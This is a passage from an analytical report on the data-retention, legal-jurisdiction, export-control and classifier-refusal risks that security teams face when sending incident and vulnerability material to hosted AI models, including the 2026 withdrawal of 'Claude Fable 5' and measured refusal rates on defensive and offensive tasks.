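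Redaction may not work at all for vulnerability data. Kapelinski and colleagues explain that even a flaw's name greatly narrows an attacker's search, but a report with the vulnerabilities removed has no analytical value. Exploits and unpublished source code have the same problem, because the model has to examine the sensitive part.

Redaction works best when the task needs only a few facts. *WiFiPenTester* (Al-Sinani and Mitchell, 2026) describes a tool for testing wireless networks that is designed around this idea. The tool scans nearby networks, extracts a few fields for each, such as encryption type, signal strength and number of connected devices, and asks a model to rank the networks as targets. The tester sees the full prompt and must approve it. Recorded traffic, connected devices' identifiers and cracked passwords stay on the tester's machine. When the model drafts the final report,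 it receives only the outcome, for example that the test recovered a passphrase.

The ranking prompt still includes each network's name and the hardware address of its access point, which public databases can often match to a location. Pseudonyms would have worked equally well for ranking. Al-Sinani and Mitchell, who used OpenAI's GPT-4o-mini in their experiments, acknowledge that the remaining details may reveal a network's layout or weaknesses. They suggest using a local model to avoid sending these details.

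### Which material should stay local

A victim should revoke stolen credentials anyway, which makes any copy at the provider worthless. But a team first has to know which credentials to revoke, and that is often what it wants the model to find out, as Hugging Face did. It could revoke everything before sending the first prompt, but that would interrupt its own services. Owners are also often slow to revoke credentials. According to daily.dev, a news site for developers, GitGuardian found that 64% of the valid secrets that leaked in 2022 were still unrevoked in 2026. Many of those owners may never have learned of the leak, though, and a team in the middle of an investigation would surely act faster.

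Encryption protects a prompt only until it reaches the provider's gateway. A contract can limit what the provider stores and give the customer a claim after a breach, but a leaked exploit can still do harm.

The best objection is that many companies already keep their logs with a cloud vendor. If Microsoft stores a company's logs and also hosts the model that reads them, no new company sees the data. Hugging Face also brought outside forensic specialists into its investigation. A large provider may also guard its systems better than the customer does. During a break-in, the team knows an intruder has been in the victim's own network, so a local model belongs on a separate, clean machine.

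These objections are convincing for ordinary logs after redaction, and public threat reports and widely shared malware samples never needed protection. The objections are much weaker for flaws that have no fix yet, because redaction removes the details that matter and the owner cannot quickly end the danger. Raw evidence from a break-in that is still under way, such as copies of disks and memory, should also stay local, since nobody yet knows which secrets it contains. Keys that take weeks to replace, such as those built into devices, should stay local too. Whether a client's data can go to an AI provider depends on the contract, and a tester whose contract doesn't allow it has to run a model locally or work without one.

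## What providers store and who can read it

When a team sends material to a hosted model, the provider's terms determine how long the provider keeps a copy and who may read it. Providers store prompts and replies to detect misuse and to support features such as resumable conversations. OpenAI calls the data it keeps for the first purpose "abuse monitoring logs" and for the second "application state". Each has its own deletion rules, so a customer who checks only the rules for abuse monitoring logs may overlook another copy.

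In late 2026 the main providers kept these records of business customers' API traffic to look for misuse:

| Service | Prompts that no classifier has flagged | Flagged prompts |
|---|---|---|
| OpenAI's API | Up to 30 days | Longer if OpenAI needs them to protect its services or other people |
| Anthropic's API | Up to 30 days | Up to two years, and the classifier's scores up to seven |
| Google's own models on Google Cloud | No abuse log for most models | Up to 90 days |

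OpenAI and Anthropic also keep data for longer when the law requires it. According to *How long do you store my organization’s data?*, Anthropic keeps data that accompanies feedback for five years. If an analyst clicks the thumbs-down button on a poor malware analysis, Anthropic may therefore keep that material for five years.

Google's terms depend on the contract and the model. According to Google Cloud's *Google models not designated as "Google Frontier Models" or "Advanced AI"*, customers who have signed a master agreement instead of accepting the standard online terms are exempt from the 90-day log by default. But Google logs everything and keeps it for up to 30 days when customers use certain models from other companies, including every version of Claude Fable and OpenAI's GPT Astra and Sol. It does the same for some older Claude models if the customer uses them under Anthropic's verified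 access programme for security work. Customers who manage their own encryption keys can't use them to block Google's access to these logs.

Authorised Google employees may also read flagged prompts and ask the customer for an explanation, and Google may suspend a customer who doesn't resolve the problem. This is a problem for security teams because the classifiers are designed to detect the exploits and malware in their prompts. Their most sensitive prompts are probably the most likely to be stored longest and read by a reviewer. It is unclear how often this happens to legitimate work, because a classifier can block a request without the provider treating it as a policy violation.

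### Storage and training

OpenAI, Google and Anthropic all store prompts, even when they don't train on them. Customers often ask whether a provider trains on their data, and may take a "no" to mean that it doesn't keep the data either. OpenAI has not trained on API data since March 2023 unless the customer opts in. Google needs the customer's permission to train on their data, and Anthropic says it has never trained on business customers' data without permission.

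Training on user data and storing it in logs carry different risks. A model can repeat something from its training data to a stranger, and its developer can't simply delete a sentence from the weights. A log entry doesn't affect the model's replies and is easy to delete, but until it is deleted, an employee may read it, a thief may copy it or a court may demand it. *Comparing OpenAI and Anthropic's Data Retention Policies*, an article from the education company DeepLearning.AI, calls "we won't train on your data" and "we don't have your data" different promises. A researcher with an unpublished exploit needs the second promise at least as much as the first.

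### What zero data retention covers

Under a zero data retention (ZDR) agreement, the provider stores no prompts or outputs once it has processed a request. OpenAI offers this only to customers it approves. With the equivalent setting on Amazon's Bedrock service, AWS neither writes the data to durable storage nor shares it with the model's developer.

ZDR doesn't change how the provider processes a prompt, so it doesn't prevent refusals and can't stop an intruder who is already watching the provider's systems. Even with ZDR enabled, OpenAI still stores files that customers upload through its file service and conversations they save on its servers. A responder who uploads a log as a file, instead of pasting it into a prompt, leaves a copy there until someone deletes it or it expires. If the model calls an outside company's tool, that company's retention rules apply to whatever the tool receives.

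OpenAI also makes smaller exceptions. It may keep encrypted intermediate results from a prompt for up to 24 hours to process repeated text faster. It also keeps images that its scanner flags as possible child sexual abuse material because, according to OpenAI's *Offering Zero Data Retention for frontier models* (2026), it has a legal duty to report them.

Google leaves more of the work to the customer. Google Cloud's *Gemini Enterprise Agent Platform and zero data retention* lists settings that customers have to change and features they have to avoid. One of its interfaces stores prompts and replies unless the customer opts out in each request. A feature that lets models use Google Search keeps queries for up to three days, and customers can't turn that storage off. CodeMender, Google's agent for finding and fixing software flaws, stores snippets of the customer's source code while a scan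 is in progress, for up to seven days, so unpublished code could be stored even if the customer has all the right contracts.

A provider can also withdraw ZDR. OpenAI's terms let it end ZDR on a model for a particular customer, after written notice, if this is reasonably necessary to investigate or prevent "severe risk activity". OpenAI may then store that customer's flagged content and have people review it. In June 2026, Anthropic ended ZDR on its newest models for all customers.

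### The dispute over Claude Fable 5

On 9 June Anthropic released Claude Fable 5 to the public and Claude Mythos 5 to approved partners. Both use the same underlying model, but Fable has more safeguards. Anthropic required data from this "Mythos-class" tier to be kept for 30 days on every platform, including its partners' clouds, because some attacks show up only across many requests. The rule made no difference to consumers, whose conversations Anthropic already stored. According to Forrester's *How Fable 5 And Mythos 5 Change AI Security, Data Retention* (2026), it overrode companies' existing zero-data-retention (ZDR) agreements and allowed no opt-out.

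The override applied only to traffic for the new models. Customers could keep ZDR on older Claude models, or turn on retention in one workspace without changing the others.

Under Anthropic's *Data retention practices for Covered Models*, no employee can read the stored data by default. A small group of approved reviewers can open a conversation through a controlled process, for example after an automated system flags it. Each access goes into a log that the reviewers cannot alter. Anthropic deletes the data automatically after 30 days unless its systems have flagged it or the law requires otherwise. Anthropic's *Covered Models*, which includes the November release Fable 5.2, now describes 30 days as the minimum retention period.

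These are fairly strict controls on employees, but Anthropic decides what to flag. *Comparing OpenAI and Anthropic’s Data Retention Policies* says customers don't know when Anthropic might change its definition of unsafe use, which would also change whose prompts reviewers may read. This is a particular concern for penetration testers, because a new definition could expose a client's data even if the tester's work stayed the same.

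Amazon's customers also lost the guarantee that their prompts would stay within AWS, where the model's developer would never see them. According to InfoQ (2026), every earlier model on Bedrock had come with that guarantee. It had helped Bedrock pass companies' legal and security reviews. In its launch announcement, AWS warned customers who turned on retention that their data would "leave AWS's data and security boundary". Security analysts at Securosis argued that this reduced Bedrock to Anthropic's own service with fewer features. By the release of Fable 5.1, AWS had restored that boundary and was keeping the logs itself. Google still requires Fable 5 customers to share the data with Anthropic, although Anthropic says the retained copy stays in Google's cloud.

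Microsoft was the most prominent reported objector. On 10 June The Verge, citing unnamed sources, reported that Microsoft was limiting its employees' use of Fable 5 while its lawyers assessed the rule, because of concerns about customer data and confidential information. Reuters repeated the report in a story by Babu but had no confirmation from either company. TechRepublic's *Microsoft Restricts Claude Fable 5 Access Amid AI Safety Review* (2026) added that the restriction was not an outright ban. The evidence for the restriction therefore comes from The Verge's sources, and the early coverage could not report how the legal review ended. Microsoft also sells access to Fable 5 through its own cloud, so restricting its staff's use would not have meant that it considered the model unsuitable for every customer.

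A better-documented refusal came from the ARC Prize Foundation, which tests models' abstract reasoning. *Claude’s Benchmark Problems* reports that the foundation declined to run its verified tests on Fable 5. The foundation requires a ZDR agreement from every provider it tests because its private questions lose their value if they leak, and vulnerability researchers are in a similar position.

*Comparing OpenAI and Anthropic's Data Retention Policies* reports that many businesses declined to use the model but gives no number. Anthropic's *Developing Enterprise Frontier Safeguards with our customers*, which draws on talks with more than 100 companies, describes their objections. Some would have to notify all their own customers and amend their contracts if Anthropic stored their data. Others handle material that only certain people may see, such as privileged legal documents, and wanted their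 own staff to do any reviewing. Security firms that work under confidentiality agreements would face both problems.

In a risk report in August, Anthropic called the rule "a decision we believe will be unpopular" and saw a real risk to its business if competitors didn't follow, according to Axios' *OpenAI previews zero-retention safety system as Anthropic requires data logs*. The rule had been in force for two months by then, and the reaction had already begun. The following week OpenAI promised to keep offering ZDR on its most capable models and previewed Private Safety Processing, a system for monitoring ZDR customers without letting its staff read their prompts. On 1 September Anthropic backed down and offered eligible customers ZDR on Fable 5 and 5.1 until it could provide Enterprise Frontier Safeguards, which keep the monitored data in the customer's own cloud.

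### When a court orders a provider to keep its logs

A court can stop a provider from deleting data it has promised to delete. The New York Times is suing OpenAI for copyright infringement, alleging in part that OpenAI's models reproduce its articles word for word, so logs of the models' replies are possible evidence. On 13 May 2025 Magistrate Judge Ona Wang ordered OpenAI to preserve all output logs "that would otherwise be deleted" (quoted by Willison). Maatman, Donoho and Ryan report in *New York Federal Court’s OpenAI Discovery Orders Provide Key Insights For Companies* that the order applied even to data that users had asked OpenAI to delete or had a legal right to erase. A few days later, Wang refused a request to reconsider the order.

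The order covered the ChatGPT Free, Plus, Pro and Team plans and the API, according to OpenAI's *How we’re responding to The New York Times’ data demands* (2025). It did not affect ChatGPT Enterprise or Edu, or API customers using zero data retention (ZDR) endpoints. The court had clarified on 27 May that the order excluded Enterprise, but ZDR customers were better protected because OpenAI had no stored data of theirs to preserve. That protection presumably did not apply to anything they stored through features that ZDR doesn't cover.

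OpenAI's duty to preserve new logs ended on 26 September 2025, under an agreement that the court approved on 9 October. The *Stipulation and Order to Terminate OpenAI’s Ongoing Obligations Under the Preservation Order* (U.S. District Court for the Southern District of New York, 2025) still required OpenAI to keep the data it had already set aside, except for requests from the European Economic Area, Switzerland and the United Kingdom. OpenAI also had to keep preserving output for accounts linked to a list of web domains, most of them apparently news sites. A U.S. customer who used the API in June 2025 could have expected OpenAI to delete the output by the end of July, but OpenAI was still holding such data in October, with access limited to a small legal and security team.

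Preserving logs does not in itself disclose them to anyone else. But in March 2026 Wang ordered OpenAI to hand over 88 million output logs that predate its filter against reproducing protected text, according to Bloomberg Law's *New York Times Wins Bid for OpenAI President’s Diary in IP Suit* (2026). These may not be the same logs that OpenAI preserved in 2025, but the ruling shows that a customer's stored output could be given to the provider's opponent in a lawsuit unrelated to the customer.

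A litigation hold keeps a security team's data for months longer than planned, and each transfer to lawyers or experts creates another copy. This is a larger risk than the plaintiff's own interest in the data, since a copyright plaintiff is unlikely to care about one company's break-in. Even a hold on outputs alone can preserve secrets, because a model that explains a server log usually repeats host names and may repeat a token.

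### Who should hold the log

The provider's log is another copy of the evidence that a security team must protect, on systems the team does not run. If someone steals the log, Anthropic commits to notifying the customer under the terms of their agreement. The customer then has to work out what its prompts contained and whom else to inform. A penetration-testing firm that used the service for twenty clients might need to contact all of them. It would also need its own record of what it sent and when.

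Security teams also need such records in their daily work. If an agent finds a password and then logs in to another server, the team must be able to reconstruct what the agent did and check the agent's conclusions against the evidence. Hugging Face's investigation would have been impossible without logs. OpenAI also expects ZDR customers to use information in their own systems when they investigate a safety alert. The objection to retention is therefore mainly about who holds the logs. The companies that Anthropic consulted wanted the data under their own encryption keys and access rules. Wells Fargo was among the banks in the industry group that took part.

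Self-hosting gives a team that control, but a court can still reach the logs, because a litigant can demand them from the team directly. Maatman and colleagues advise companies to keep an inventory of their prompts and outputs, and to build systems that can pause deletion when a lawsuit requires it. The team would receive the demand and could contest it, whereas OpenAI's customers had to rely largely on OpenAI to argue for them. The team also has to set its own deletion period. If it never deletes its logs, a thief or a court could take more than a provider with a 30-day limit would have held.

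## Jurisdiction, export controls and the power to switch a model off

Governments, like courts and litigants, can demand a provider's logs, but they can also make the provider withdraw a model. In June 2026 the US Commerce Department did this to Anthropic, and customers worldwide lost access to its two newest models within hours.

Buyers and sellers use "sovereignty" for three different things. Data residency is where the data is stored. Jurisdiction determines which governments can compel someone to disclose it, and "data sovereignty" usually covers both. Operational sovereignty is control over what an AI system may do and whether it stays available. Suppose a hospital in Lyon sends its security alerts to an American company's model in a Paris data centre. The alerts never leave France, but an American judge can still order the company to disclose any copy it has kept, and the company can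 restrict or withdraw the model without asking the hospital.

### How the CLOUD Act applies to data in Europe

The CLOUD Act of March 2018 grew out of a dispute over e-mails that Microsoft stored in Ireland. Microsoft objected that handing them to US investigators would break EU and Irish privacy law, and an appeals court sided with the company in 2016. Congress passed the Act while the case was before the Supreme Court. According to the Congressional Research Service's *Law Enforcement Access to Overseas Data Under the CLOUD Act*, the Court ruled in April 2018 that the Act had made the case moot.

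To get the contents of someone's files, investigators must show a judge probable cause, meaning good reason to believe that the files contain evidence of a crime. They then serve the judge's warrant on the provider, not the customer. The Act's central provision, the U.S. Code's *Required preservation and disclosure of communications and records* (2021), requires the provider to disclose data in its "possession, custody, or control", whether stored inside or outside the United States. An American company that can retrieve a file from its Paris data centre therefore cannot refuse to disclose it on the grounds that it is stored abroad.

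According to the law firm WSGR, the provider has 14 days to ask the court to cancel or change the order. It must reasonably believe that the person concerned is neither a US person nor a US resident, and that disclosure may break the law of a "qualifying" country, which must have signed an executive agreement with the United States. In June 2025, Richard Salgado was still urging the US government to finalise one with the European Union (*Witness Statement of Richard Salgado and Exhibits*, 2025). Without an agreement, the provider can't use this procedure to defend the hospital in Lyon, though it can still ask the judge to consider the conflict with French law. If the judge upholds the warrant, the provider has to comply.

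The U.S. Department of Justice says the Act gave investigators no new authority and only restored the practice from before 2016. It adds that the Budapest Convention, a treaty on cybercrime, requires every member state to have the same power over providers on its territory. The EU adopted similar rules in 2023. Moving from an American provider to a German one therefore changes which governments can demand the hospital's data, but at least one government will still be able to demand it.

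The Act covers companies that store or process other people's data over a network, and a hosted model API seems to fit that description. But a warrant for stored data yields only what the provider has stored. A provider that keeps prompts for 30 days could have a month of the hospital's alerts to hand over, while one with a zero data retention agreement should have almost none, so the retention terms matter more here than the server's location. Customers can encrypt stored files with a key the provider doesn't have, but they can't do this with the prompts they send to an ordinary hosted model.

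### What the providers told the French parliament

The best-known statement about the Act comes from Anton Carniaux, then Microsoft France's director of public and legal affairs. The Sénat's *Convocation* (2025) sets his hearing for 10 June 2025, though some press reports date the testimony to 18 June. The senators asked whether Microsoft could promise never to pass data from UGAP, the central purchasing body for French schools and town halls, to the US government without the French authorities' consent. heise online's *Not sovereign* reports that Carniaux could not guarantee this under oath.

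Carniaux added that such a transfer had never happened. Microsoft checks each request and can refuse those that are formally unfounded, but it must comply with the rest and needs the American authorities' permission to tell the customer. The question he was asked was narrower than the headlines implied when they presented his answer as an admission about all European data. But the answer follows from the Act and would presumably have been the same for a private company.

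An inquiry by France's lower house questioned Microsoft, Amazon and Google under oath in May 2026. In the Assemblée nationale's *Compte rendu n° 44* (2026), Microsoft repeated that it had never disclosed a European public administration's data, but mentioned one case in three years involving a private company. Amazon said it had never given the US government data belonging to companies or governments outside the United States. Google's representative said the company complies with court orders, whether the judge is French, German or American.

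Philippe Latombe, who chaired the inquiry, doubted that such exact counts could include secret orders. Amazon insisted that its count did. Google said that American rules let it publish only broad ranges, such as 0 to 500, for orders under the Foreign Intelligence Surveillance Act, which is used for intelligence gathering rather than criminal cases. The figures suggest that an ordinary European company runs little risk of losing its data this way. They are less reassuring for a foreign ministry or an army, because an intelligence service would obviously want a report on how intruders got into such an organisation's networks.

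France's answer is a security certification called SecNumCloud, which American-owned companies can't obtain. Two French-controlled clouds, Bleu and S3NS, run Microsoft's and Google's technology without giving either company control. The Senate inquiry report *L'urgence d'agir pour éviter la sortie de route* had already called the state's choice of Microsoft to host the national health-data platform a clear error, "if not a political fault", and asked for a host beyond the reach of foreign law. Such a host would solve the disclosure problem but would still depend on foreign developers for any closed models it offered.

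### The withdrawal of Fable 5 and Mythos 5

The withdrawal came three days after the two models' release. Amazon researchers had found a way around Fable 5's safeguards. According to Anthropic's *Redeploying Fable 5* (2026), the researchers' prompts got the model to identify several software vulnerabilities and, in one case, write code that demonstrated an exploit. The government learned of the researchers' report, and at 5:21 p.m. on Friday 12 June Anthropic received a letter from the Commerce Department.

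It was an "is informed" letter, which tells one company that it needs a licence to export a particular item. The requirement starts at once, without public consultation. *A Kill Switch for Frontier AI* (Rozenshtein, 2026) explains that the department had previously used such letters to block sales of advanced chips to China. This one covered access by any foreign national, inside or outside the United States, including Anthropic's own foreign employees. Anthropic had no reliable way to check its users' nationality, so it shut off both models for everyone that evening.

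| Who lost access | Why | When it returned |
|---|---|---|
| Fable 5 customers abroad | The order barred them | 1 July |
| Fable 5 customers in the US | Anthropic could not separate Americans from foreigners | 1 July |
| Fable 5 customers on AWS, Google Cloud and Microsoft's cloud | Anthropic withdrew the model there too | Shortly after 1 July |
| Organisations with approved access to Mythos 5 | Anthropic withdrew the model from everyone | From 26 June for a selected group in the US; Anthropic was still negotiating for others on 30 June |

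The approved partners had Mythos 5 for defensive security work, so the order took the strongest available tool away from people whose job was to find and fix flaws.

The two sides disagree about whether the order was necessary. David Sacks, a former White House adviser on AI, said the bypass enabled the "operability of a cyber weapon" and that Anthropic had refused to fix the problem or pull the model. Anthropic's *Statement on the US government directive to suspend access to Fable 5* (2026) objects that the government had offered only verbal evidence of a narrow technique. The company later found that every model it tested, including its own small Claude Haiku 4.5 and the Chinese model Kimi K2.7, could produce the same exploit demonstration. The Atlantic Council's *The Fable 5 shutdown and the troubling precedent it sets* reports that more than a hundred cybersecurity leaders argued in an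 open letter that Fable 5 was not uniquely dangerous. If they are right, the order deprived defenders of a good model while doing little to hinder attackers.

The Council on Foreign Relations mentions other suspected causes, including a report that Anthropic had shared a powerful version of the model with a South Korean telecommunications company without the White House's permission. It also mentions Anthropic's older quarrel with the Pentagon.

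Lawyers doubted that the department had the authority. Export rules clearly apply to the transfer of weights, but a Fable 5 customer receives only replies to prompts, never the weights. The Harvard Law Review's *Is Access to Fable an Export?* notes that the department had classed cloud computing as a service outside these rules, and had explained in 2016 that potential access to a technology does not alone count as releasing it. The department could answer that a rival can train its own model on enough of Fable's replies, so access amounts to a slow transfer of the technology.

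A legal software company sued on 23 June. The department lifted the controls on 30 June, after negotiating with Anthropic, so customers got the model back without a court ruling. Even a strong case would have been little use to a team that needed the model that week.

Fable 5 also came back with a new classifier, which blocks the Amazon researchers' technique in more than 99% of cases. Anthropic acknowledges that the classifier also flags more harmless requests during routine coding and debugging. A security team that had tested Fable 5 in early June therefore got a more restrictive model in July. Anthropic also promised the government earlier access to new models and their safeguards. The Center for American Progress, a think tank, argued in August that the government's voluntary testing scheme had become a licensing system in practice.

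### What the withdrawal showed about continuity

Claude Opus 4.8 and Anthropic's other models kept working throughout. A team whose software could switch models would have had to use a somewhat weaker one for 19 days, which is inconvenient but not disastrous. A team's own server could easily be down for as long if a part broke and nobody had a spare.

The usual precautions against an outage did not help. A customer that stored its data in Europe and bought Fable 5 from two clouds would have lost access through both at once, because the same order applied to both. The hospital in Lyon could have met every French rule on data and still been without the model on Saturday.

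This was awkward for a government promoting American AI abroad. In Axios' *Trump's AI export strategy runs into Trump's export controls* (2026), the former Trump adviser Dean Ball calls the removal of the best models from foreign use arbitrary and abrupt, and concludes that the government's export programme no longer matters to its decision makers. *Fable 5's Double Exposure* (Willing, 2026) quotes Ashish Nagar, whose company LevelAI sells an alternative AI product for customer service, warning that access to a public model "can be cut off anytime".

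American customers had already had a similar experience. In February President Trump ordered federal agencies to stop using Anthropic's models (Kahn, 2026, *Anthropic disables Fable and Mythos AI models*). The Pentagon wanted to use the models "for any lawful purpose", and Anthropic wanted exceptions for autonomous weapons and mass domestic surveillance. The dispute was over who decides what the models may do and involved no foreign law, but federal staff still lost access to them.

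### How many governments have moved

There is little public evidence that governments, armed forces or infrastructure operators have adopted local models for these reasons. Google's representative told the Assemblée nationale's inquiry that the company's fully disconnected systems, which include AI, are very successful, especially in defence and financial services, but named no customers and gave no sales figures. Microsoft told the same hearing that it offers AI models for disconnected environments. Amazon described a European cloud, launched in January 2026, that it designed to keep running even if Europe were cut off from the rest of the world. The European Commission has chosen S3NS for some of its sensitive needs.

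These examples show demand for systems that don't depend on a connection to the United States. But none shows a ministry or a power company moving its security analysis to an open-weight model, and all predate the June withdrawal. Armed forces also have an older reason to run models locally, which is that many of their networks have no outside connection and can't reach a hosted model, regardless of the law.

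### The case for operational sovereignty

David Bianco of Cisco Talos, Cisco's threat research group, uses "operational sovereignty" to mean having the final say over what an organisation's AI may do. Bianco is mainly concerned with refusals rather than governments. When a hosted model refuses to explain an exploit, an analyst has to do the work by hand while the attacker carries on, which Bianco calls a "safety penalty". A provider can also change its policy or update the model without notice, which may break a workflow that worked last month. Bianco doesn't object to safeguards but wants the organisation using the model to control them.

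The most direct remedy is to run a model on the team's own hardware, which may mean waiting months for GPUs and hiring scarce specialists. A team can instead rent capacity from a company that runs the customer's chosen model without adding filters. Dedicated capacity is often hard to get, and shared capacity may reintroduce the filters. In a hybrid design, the team keeps using a hosted model, and a gateway sends any refused prompt to a smaller local one. Bianco's most speculative idea is for companies in one industry to jointly fund and govern a shared model. They would have to agree on rules for its use, and an attack on the whole industry would make them all need it at once.

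These remedies work less well against an order like the one in June. Bianco's examples of rented capacity include Amazon's and Microsoft's platforms, so a European team that moved there would avoid the filters but still depend on a service subject to American law. The hybrid design would work better, provided the gateway also switched to the local model when the hosted one stopped responding altogether.

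Cisco sells security products, and Bianco gives no figures for how often models refuse defenders. The advice to measure refusals before buying anything is still sound, because a team that loses only two prompts a month to refusals has little reason to buy a rack of GPUs.

### What downloaded weights leave unsettled

Nobody can recall weights that a team has already copied. If Z.ai went out of business, GLM-5.2 would keep running on every server that holds it. A government could forbid an organisation to use the model, but could not switch it off remotely. A self-hosting team needs outsiders only when it wants something new, whereas a hosted customer needs the provider's cooperation for every prompt.

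The team will want new models fairly often, but the licence for GLM-5.2 covers only that release and doesn't oblige Z.ai to publish the next one or offer it on the same terms. Although an old model keeps its skills, its training data doesn't cover flaws and attack tools that appeared later. The team can make up for some of this by putting recent threat reports in the prompt, but it can't do much about a growing gap in ability if attackers move to newer models.

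Buying new hardware also depends on foreign governments. Just Security's *AI Model Outputs Demand the Attention of Export Control Agencies* notes that both the Biden and the Trump administrations restricted exports of AI chips to China and other countries of concern. A Biden-era rule would also have capped chip exports country by country, but the Commerce Department rescinded it in May 2025. Chips that a team already owns would keep working under a new restriction, but a team that planned to buy them during an emergency could need a licence.

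The strongest open-weight models come from China, so a European organisation that gives up American services for GLM-5.2 exchanges one foreign supplier for another. The switch still helps, because a supplier that has delivered the weights has less power than one that runs the service. American organisations also depend on Chinese models. Sherman (2026), in *What the OpenAI-Hugging Face incident reveals about US-China AI interdependence*, points out that an American company's models attacked Hugging Face, guardrails from another American company hindered its defence, and a Chinese model did the forensic work. The dependence was mutual, since the build of the Chinese model that Hugging Face used came from NVIDIA, an American chipmaker.

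Sherman accepts that Chinese models might contain backdoors and that they undercut American competitors, but opposes judging models as good or bad by country of origin. Sherman argues that if the United States had banned Chinese models, Hugging Face would have had only the hosted models that had already failed it. This overstates the case, because Hugging Face could also have tried an open-weight model from an American or European developer. Nobody has published a test of how well those models would have handled the same log. Sherman proposes comparing American and Chinese models on tasks designed by working defenders, which would help to answer that question.

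A security team can run a small version of that comparison itself by testing an American or European open-weight model on its own past incidents. If it keeps a copy of that model alongside GLM-5.2, the team would lose some quality under a ban on Chinese models but would still have a local model.

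## Why hosted models refuse defenders

Governments rarely cut off access to a model, but a refusal can interrupt any security task. Some refusals come from the model's training, and others come from the safety classifier that screens prompts and replies. Hugging Face's responders encountered enough refusals that they switched models during an investigation.

### How a classifier judges a request

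A cyber safety classifier scores each text by how closely it resembles the requests the classifier's developer wants to stop. The provider sets a threshold, and the system blocks any text that scores above it. A lower threshold stops more attacks but also more legitimate work. If an attacker's request and a defender's request get the same score, no threshold can separate them.

This happens often in security because, as Hugging Face pointed out, a responder's prompt may contain the same commands an attacker typed. *Cyber-Capable AI Agents* (2026) explains that a filter that evaluates only such material cannot take the sender's role into account. Requests written from scratch can be just as ambiguous. *A Content-Based Framework for Cybersecurity Refusal Decisions in Large Language Models* (2026) gives the example of a request to scan a private codebase for common flaws, which could be a routine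 check or the start of a break-in.

According to Anthropic's *Why Claude switched models in your conversation with Fable 5*, the classifier on Claude Fable 5 checks the analyst's question and anything else the model reads, including files and search results. A log full of attack commands can therefore trigger a block even if the question about it is harmless.

*The Entanglement Wall* (2026) tested how well detectors can separate harmful requests from harmless ones on the same topic. The main detectors read a model's activations, the numbers it computes while processing a prompt. With thresholds carried over from other data, they blocked most of the harmless requests. Some other classifiers blocked fewer but missed many harmful requests. Even the reference detectors blocked 9 to 18 of 70 harmless requests. These test sets don't measure how often real users are wrongly blocked, but the results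 suggest that reading the text better won't solve the whole problem. The paper suggests using evidence from outside the prompt, such as a verified role or proof that the user owns the system.

### Anthropic's four categories and the safety margin

After Fable 5 returned in July, Anthropic published a list of what its cyber classifiers should block. The list divides security work into four categories. "Dual use" work can benefit both attackers and defenders.

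| Category | Examples | Intended treatment on Fable 5 |
|---|---|---|
| Prohibited use | Writing or debugging malware, command and control, evading defences, ransomware | Block |
| High-risk dual use | Penetration testing, exploit development, finding flaws that other widely available models can't find | Block until Anthropic can limit access to known good users |
| Low-risk dual use | Scanning public systems, finding flaws that other tools already find | Allow many requests but block a large fraction |
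| Benign use | Incident response, log analysis, malware reverse engineering, fixing known flaws | Allow |

Anthropic acknowledges that defenders regularly use some of the prohibited techniques, including evading defences. It prohibits them anyway because they can do great harm and appear often in real attacks.

Anthropic deliberately blocks more than these categories suggest, including some requests that are probably harmless, so a request has to look very clearly safe to get through. It calls this buffer the "safety margin" and made it larger for Fable 5 than for any earlier model. Incident response and malware reverse engineering are on the benign list but can still be blocked, and Anthropic describes such blocks as likely false positives.

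Malware analysis shows why the margin catches benign work. Anthropic's list classes explaining a malicious program as benign and debugging one as prohibited. An analyst has to run a sample in the lab to see what it does, and if it crashes, asking why is close to asking for help debugging it.

Defensive and offensive requests are also hard to tell apart in vulnerability work. *CyberDualEval* (2026), a benchmark of 430 tasks, splits each task into three stages: security analysis, proof of concept and exploit. For a flaw in the PHP programming language, the security analysis explains that poor error handling could let a program write outside its assigned memory. The proof of concept supplies an input that triggers this. The exploit uses the flaw to do something an attacker wants, such as running commands on the server. Public code repositories use "proof of concept" and "exploit" inconsistently,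 so a developer can't rely on the label to decide what to block. A defender may need a proof of concept to check whether a patch worked.

When a cyber request to Fable 5 is blocked in Anthropic's own apps, Claude Opus 4.8, which has its own safeguards, answers instead. API customers have to set up this fallback themselves. An analyst can switch back to Fable 5 afterwards, but the material that caused the block is still in the conversation and may cause another.

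Anthropic's billing rules suggest that its cyber classifier has a higher false-positive rate than some of its others. When a classifier blocks a request before any output, Anthropic still charges for it if the block was for biology, AI development or attempts to copy the model, the areas where its false-positive rates were lowest as of September 2026. It doesn't charge for cyber blocks at that stage.

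### What a 5% error rate does to an investigation

Suppose a classifier screens 100,000 requests, 1 in 1,000 of which is malicious. It blocks 95% of malicious requests and 5% of benign ones. It then stops 95 of the 100 malicious requests and 4,995 of the 99,900 benign ones, so the benign share of all blocked requests is

4,995 / (4,995 + 95) ≈ 98%

These rates are invented, and the result depends heavily on how rare malicious requests are. If 1 request in 10 were malicious, the benign share of blocked requests would fall to about 32%. When that share is 98%, the classifier still stops nearly all the attacks, but a block is weak evidence against the person who sent the request.

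For an analyst, the 5% matters more. An AI agent may need 100 requests to work through a log. If each request has a 5% chance of being blocked, independently of the others, the chance of finishing without an interruption is

0.95^100 ≈ 0.6%

On average, the agent would meet five blocks. For an even chance of finishing uninterrupted, the false-positive rate would have to be about 0.7%.

The calculation unrealistically assumes that blocks occur independently. Agents resend earlier text at each step, so material that triggers one block may well trigger the next, while a routine log may trigger none. At the same average block rate, this clustering lets more investigations finish uninterrupted but makes the blocked ones harder to resume. The calculation also counts every block as an interruption, although a fallback model may answer immediately.

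### Measured refusal rates

*Beyond Success Rate* (Kassianik, Nelson and Singer, 2026) tested recent models as AI agents on defensive and offensive security tasks. The agents were given tools for searching logs and asked 31 questions about two break-ins at a fictional company, one involving a defaced website and the other ransomware. They also faced 39 offensive challenges, each of which required attacking a practice system to recover a hidden piece of text. Each agent attempted every task three times.

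| Model | Refusals in 93 defensive attempts | Refusals in 117 offensive attempts | Defensive score |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 5 | 117 | 88.4% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 2 | 5 | 93.9% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 0 | 106 | 91.4% |
| GPT-5.6 Terra | 0 | 39 | 92.1% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0 | 7 | 81.0% |
| DeepSeek v4 Flash | 0 | 0 | 73.0% |

On these tasks, the guardrails distinguished log investigation from attacks fairly well. Fable 5 refused every offensive challenge before using any tools, but only about 5% of the defensive attempts. Each attempt can involve many requests, so the refusal rate per request was probably much lower than in the calculation above. However, the defensive questions mainly test log searching, so they provide little evidence about reverse-engineering malware or validating exploits.

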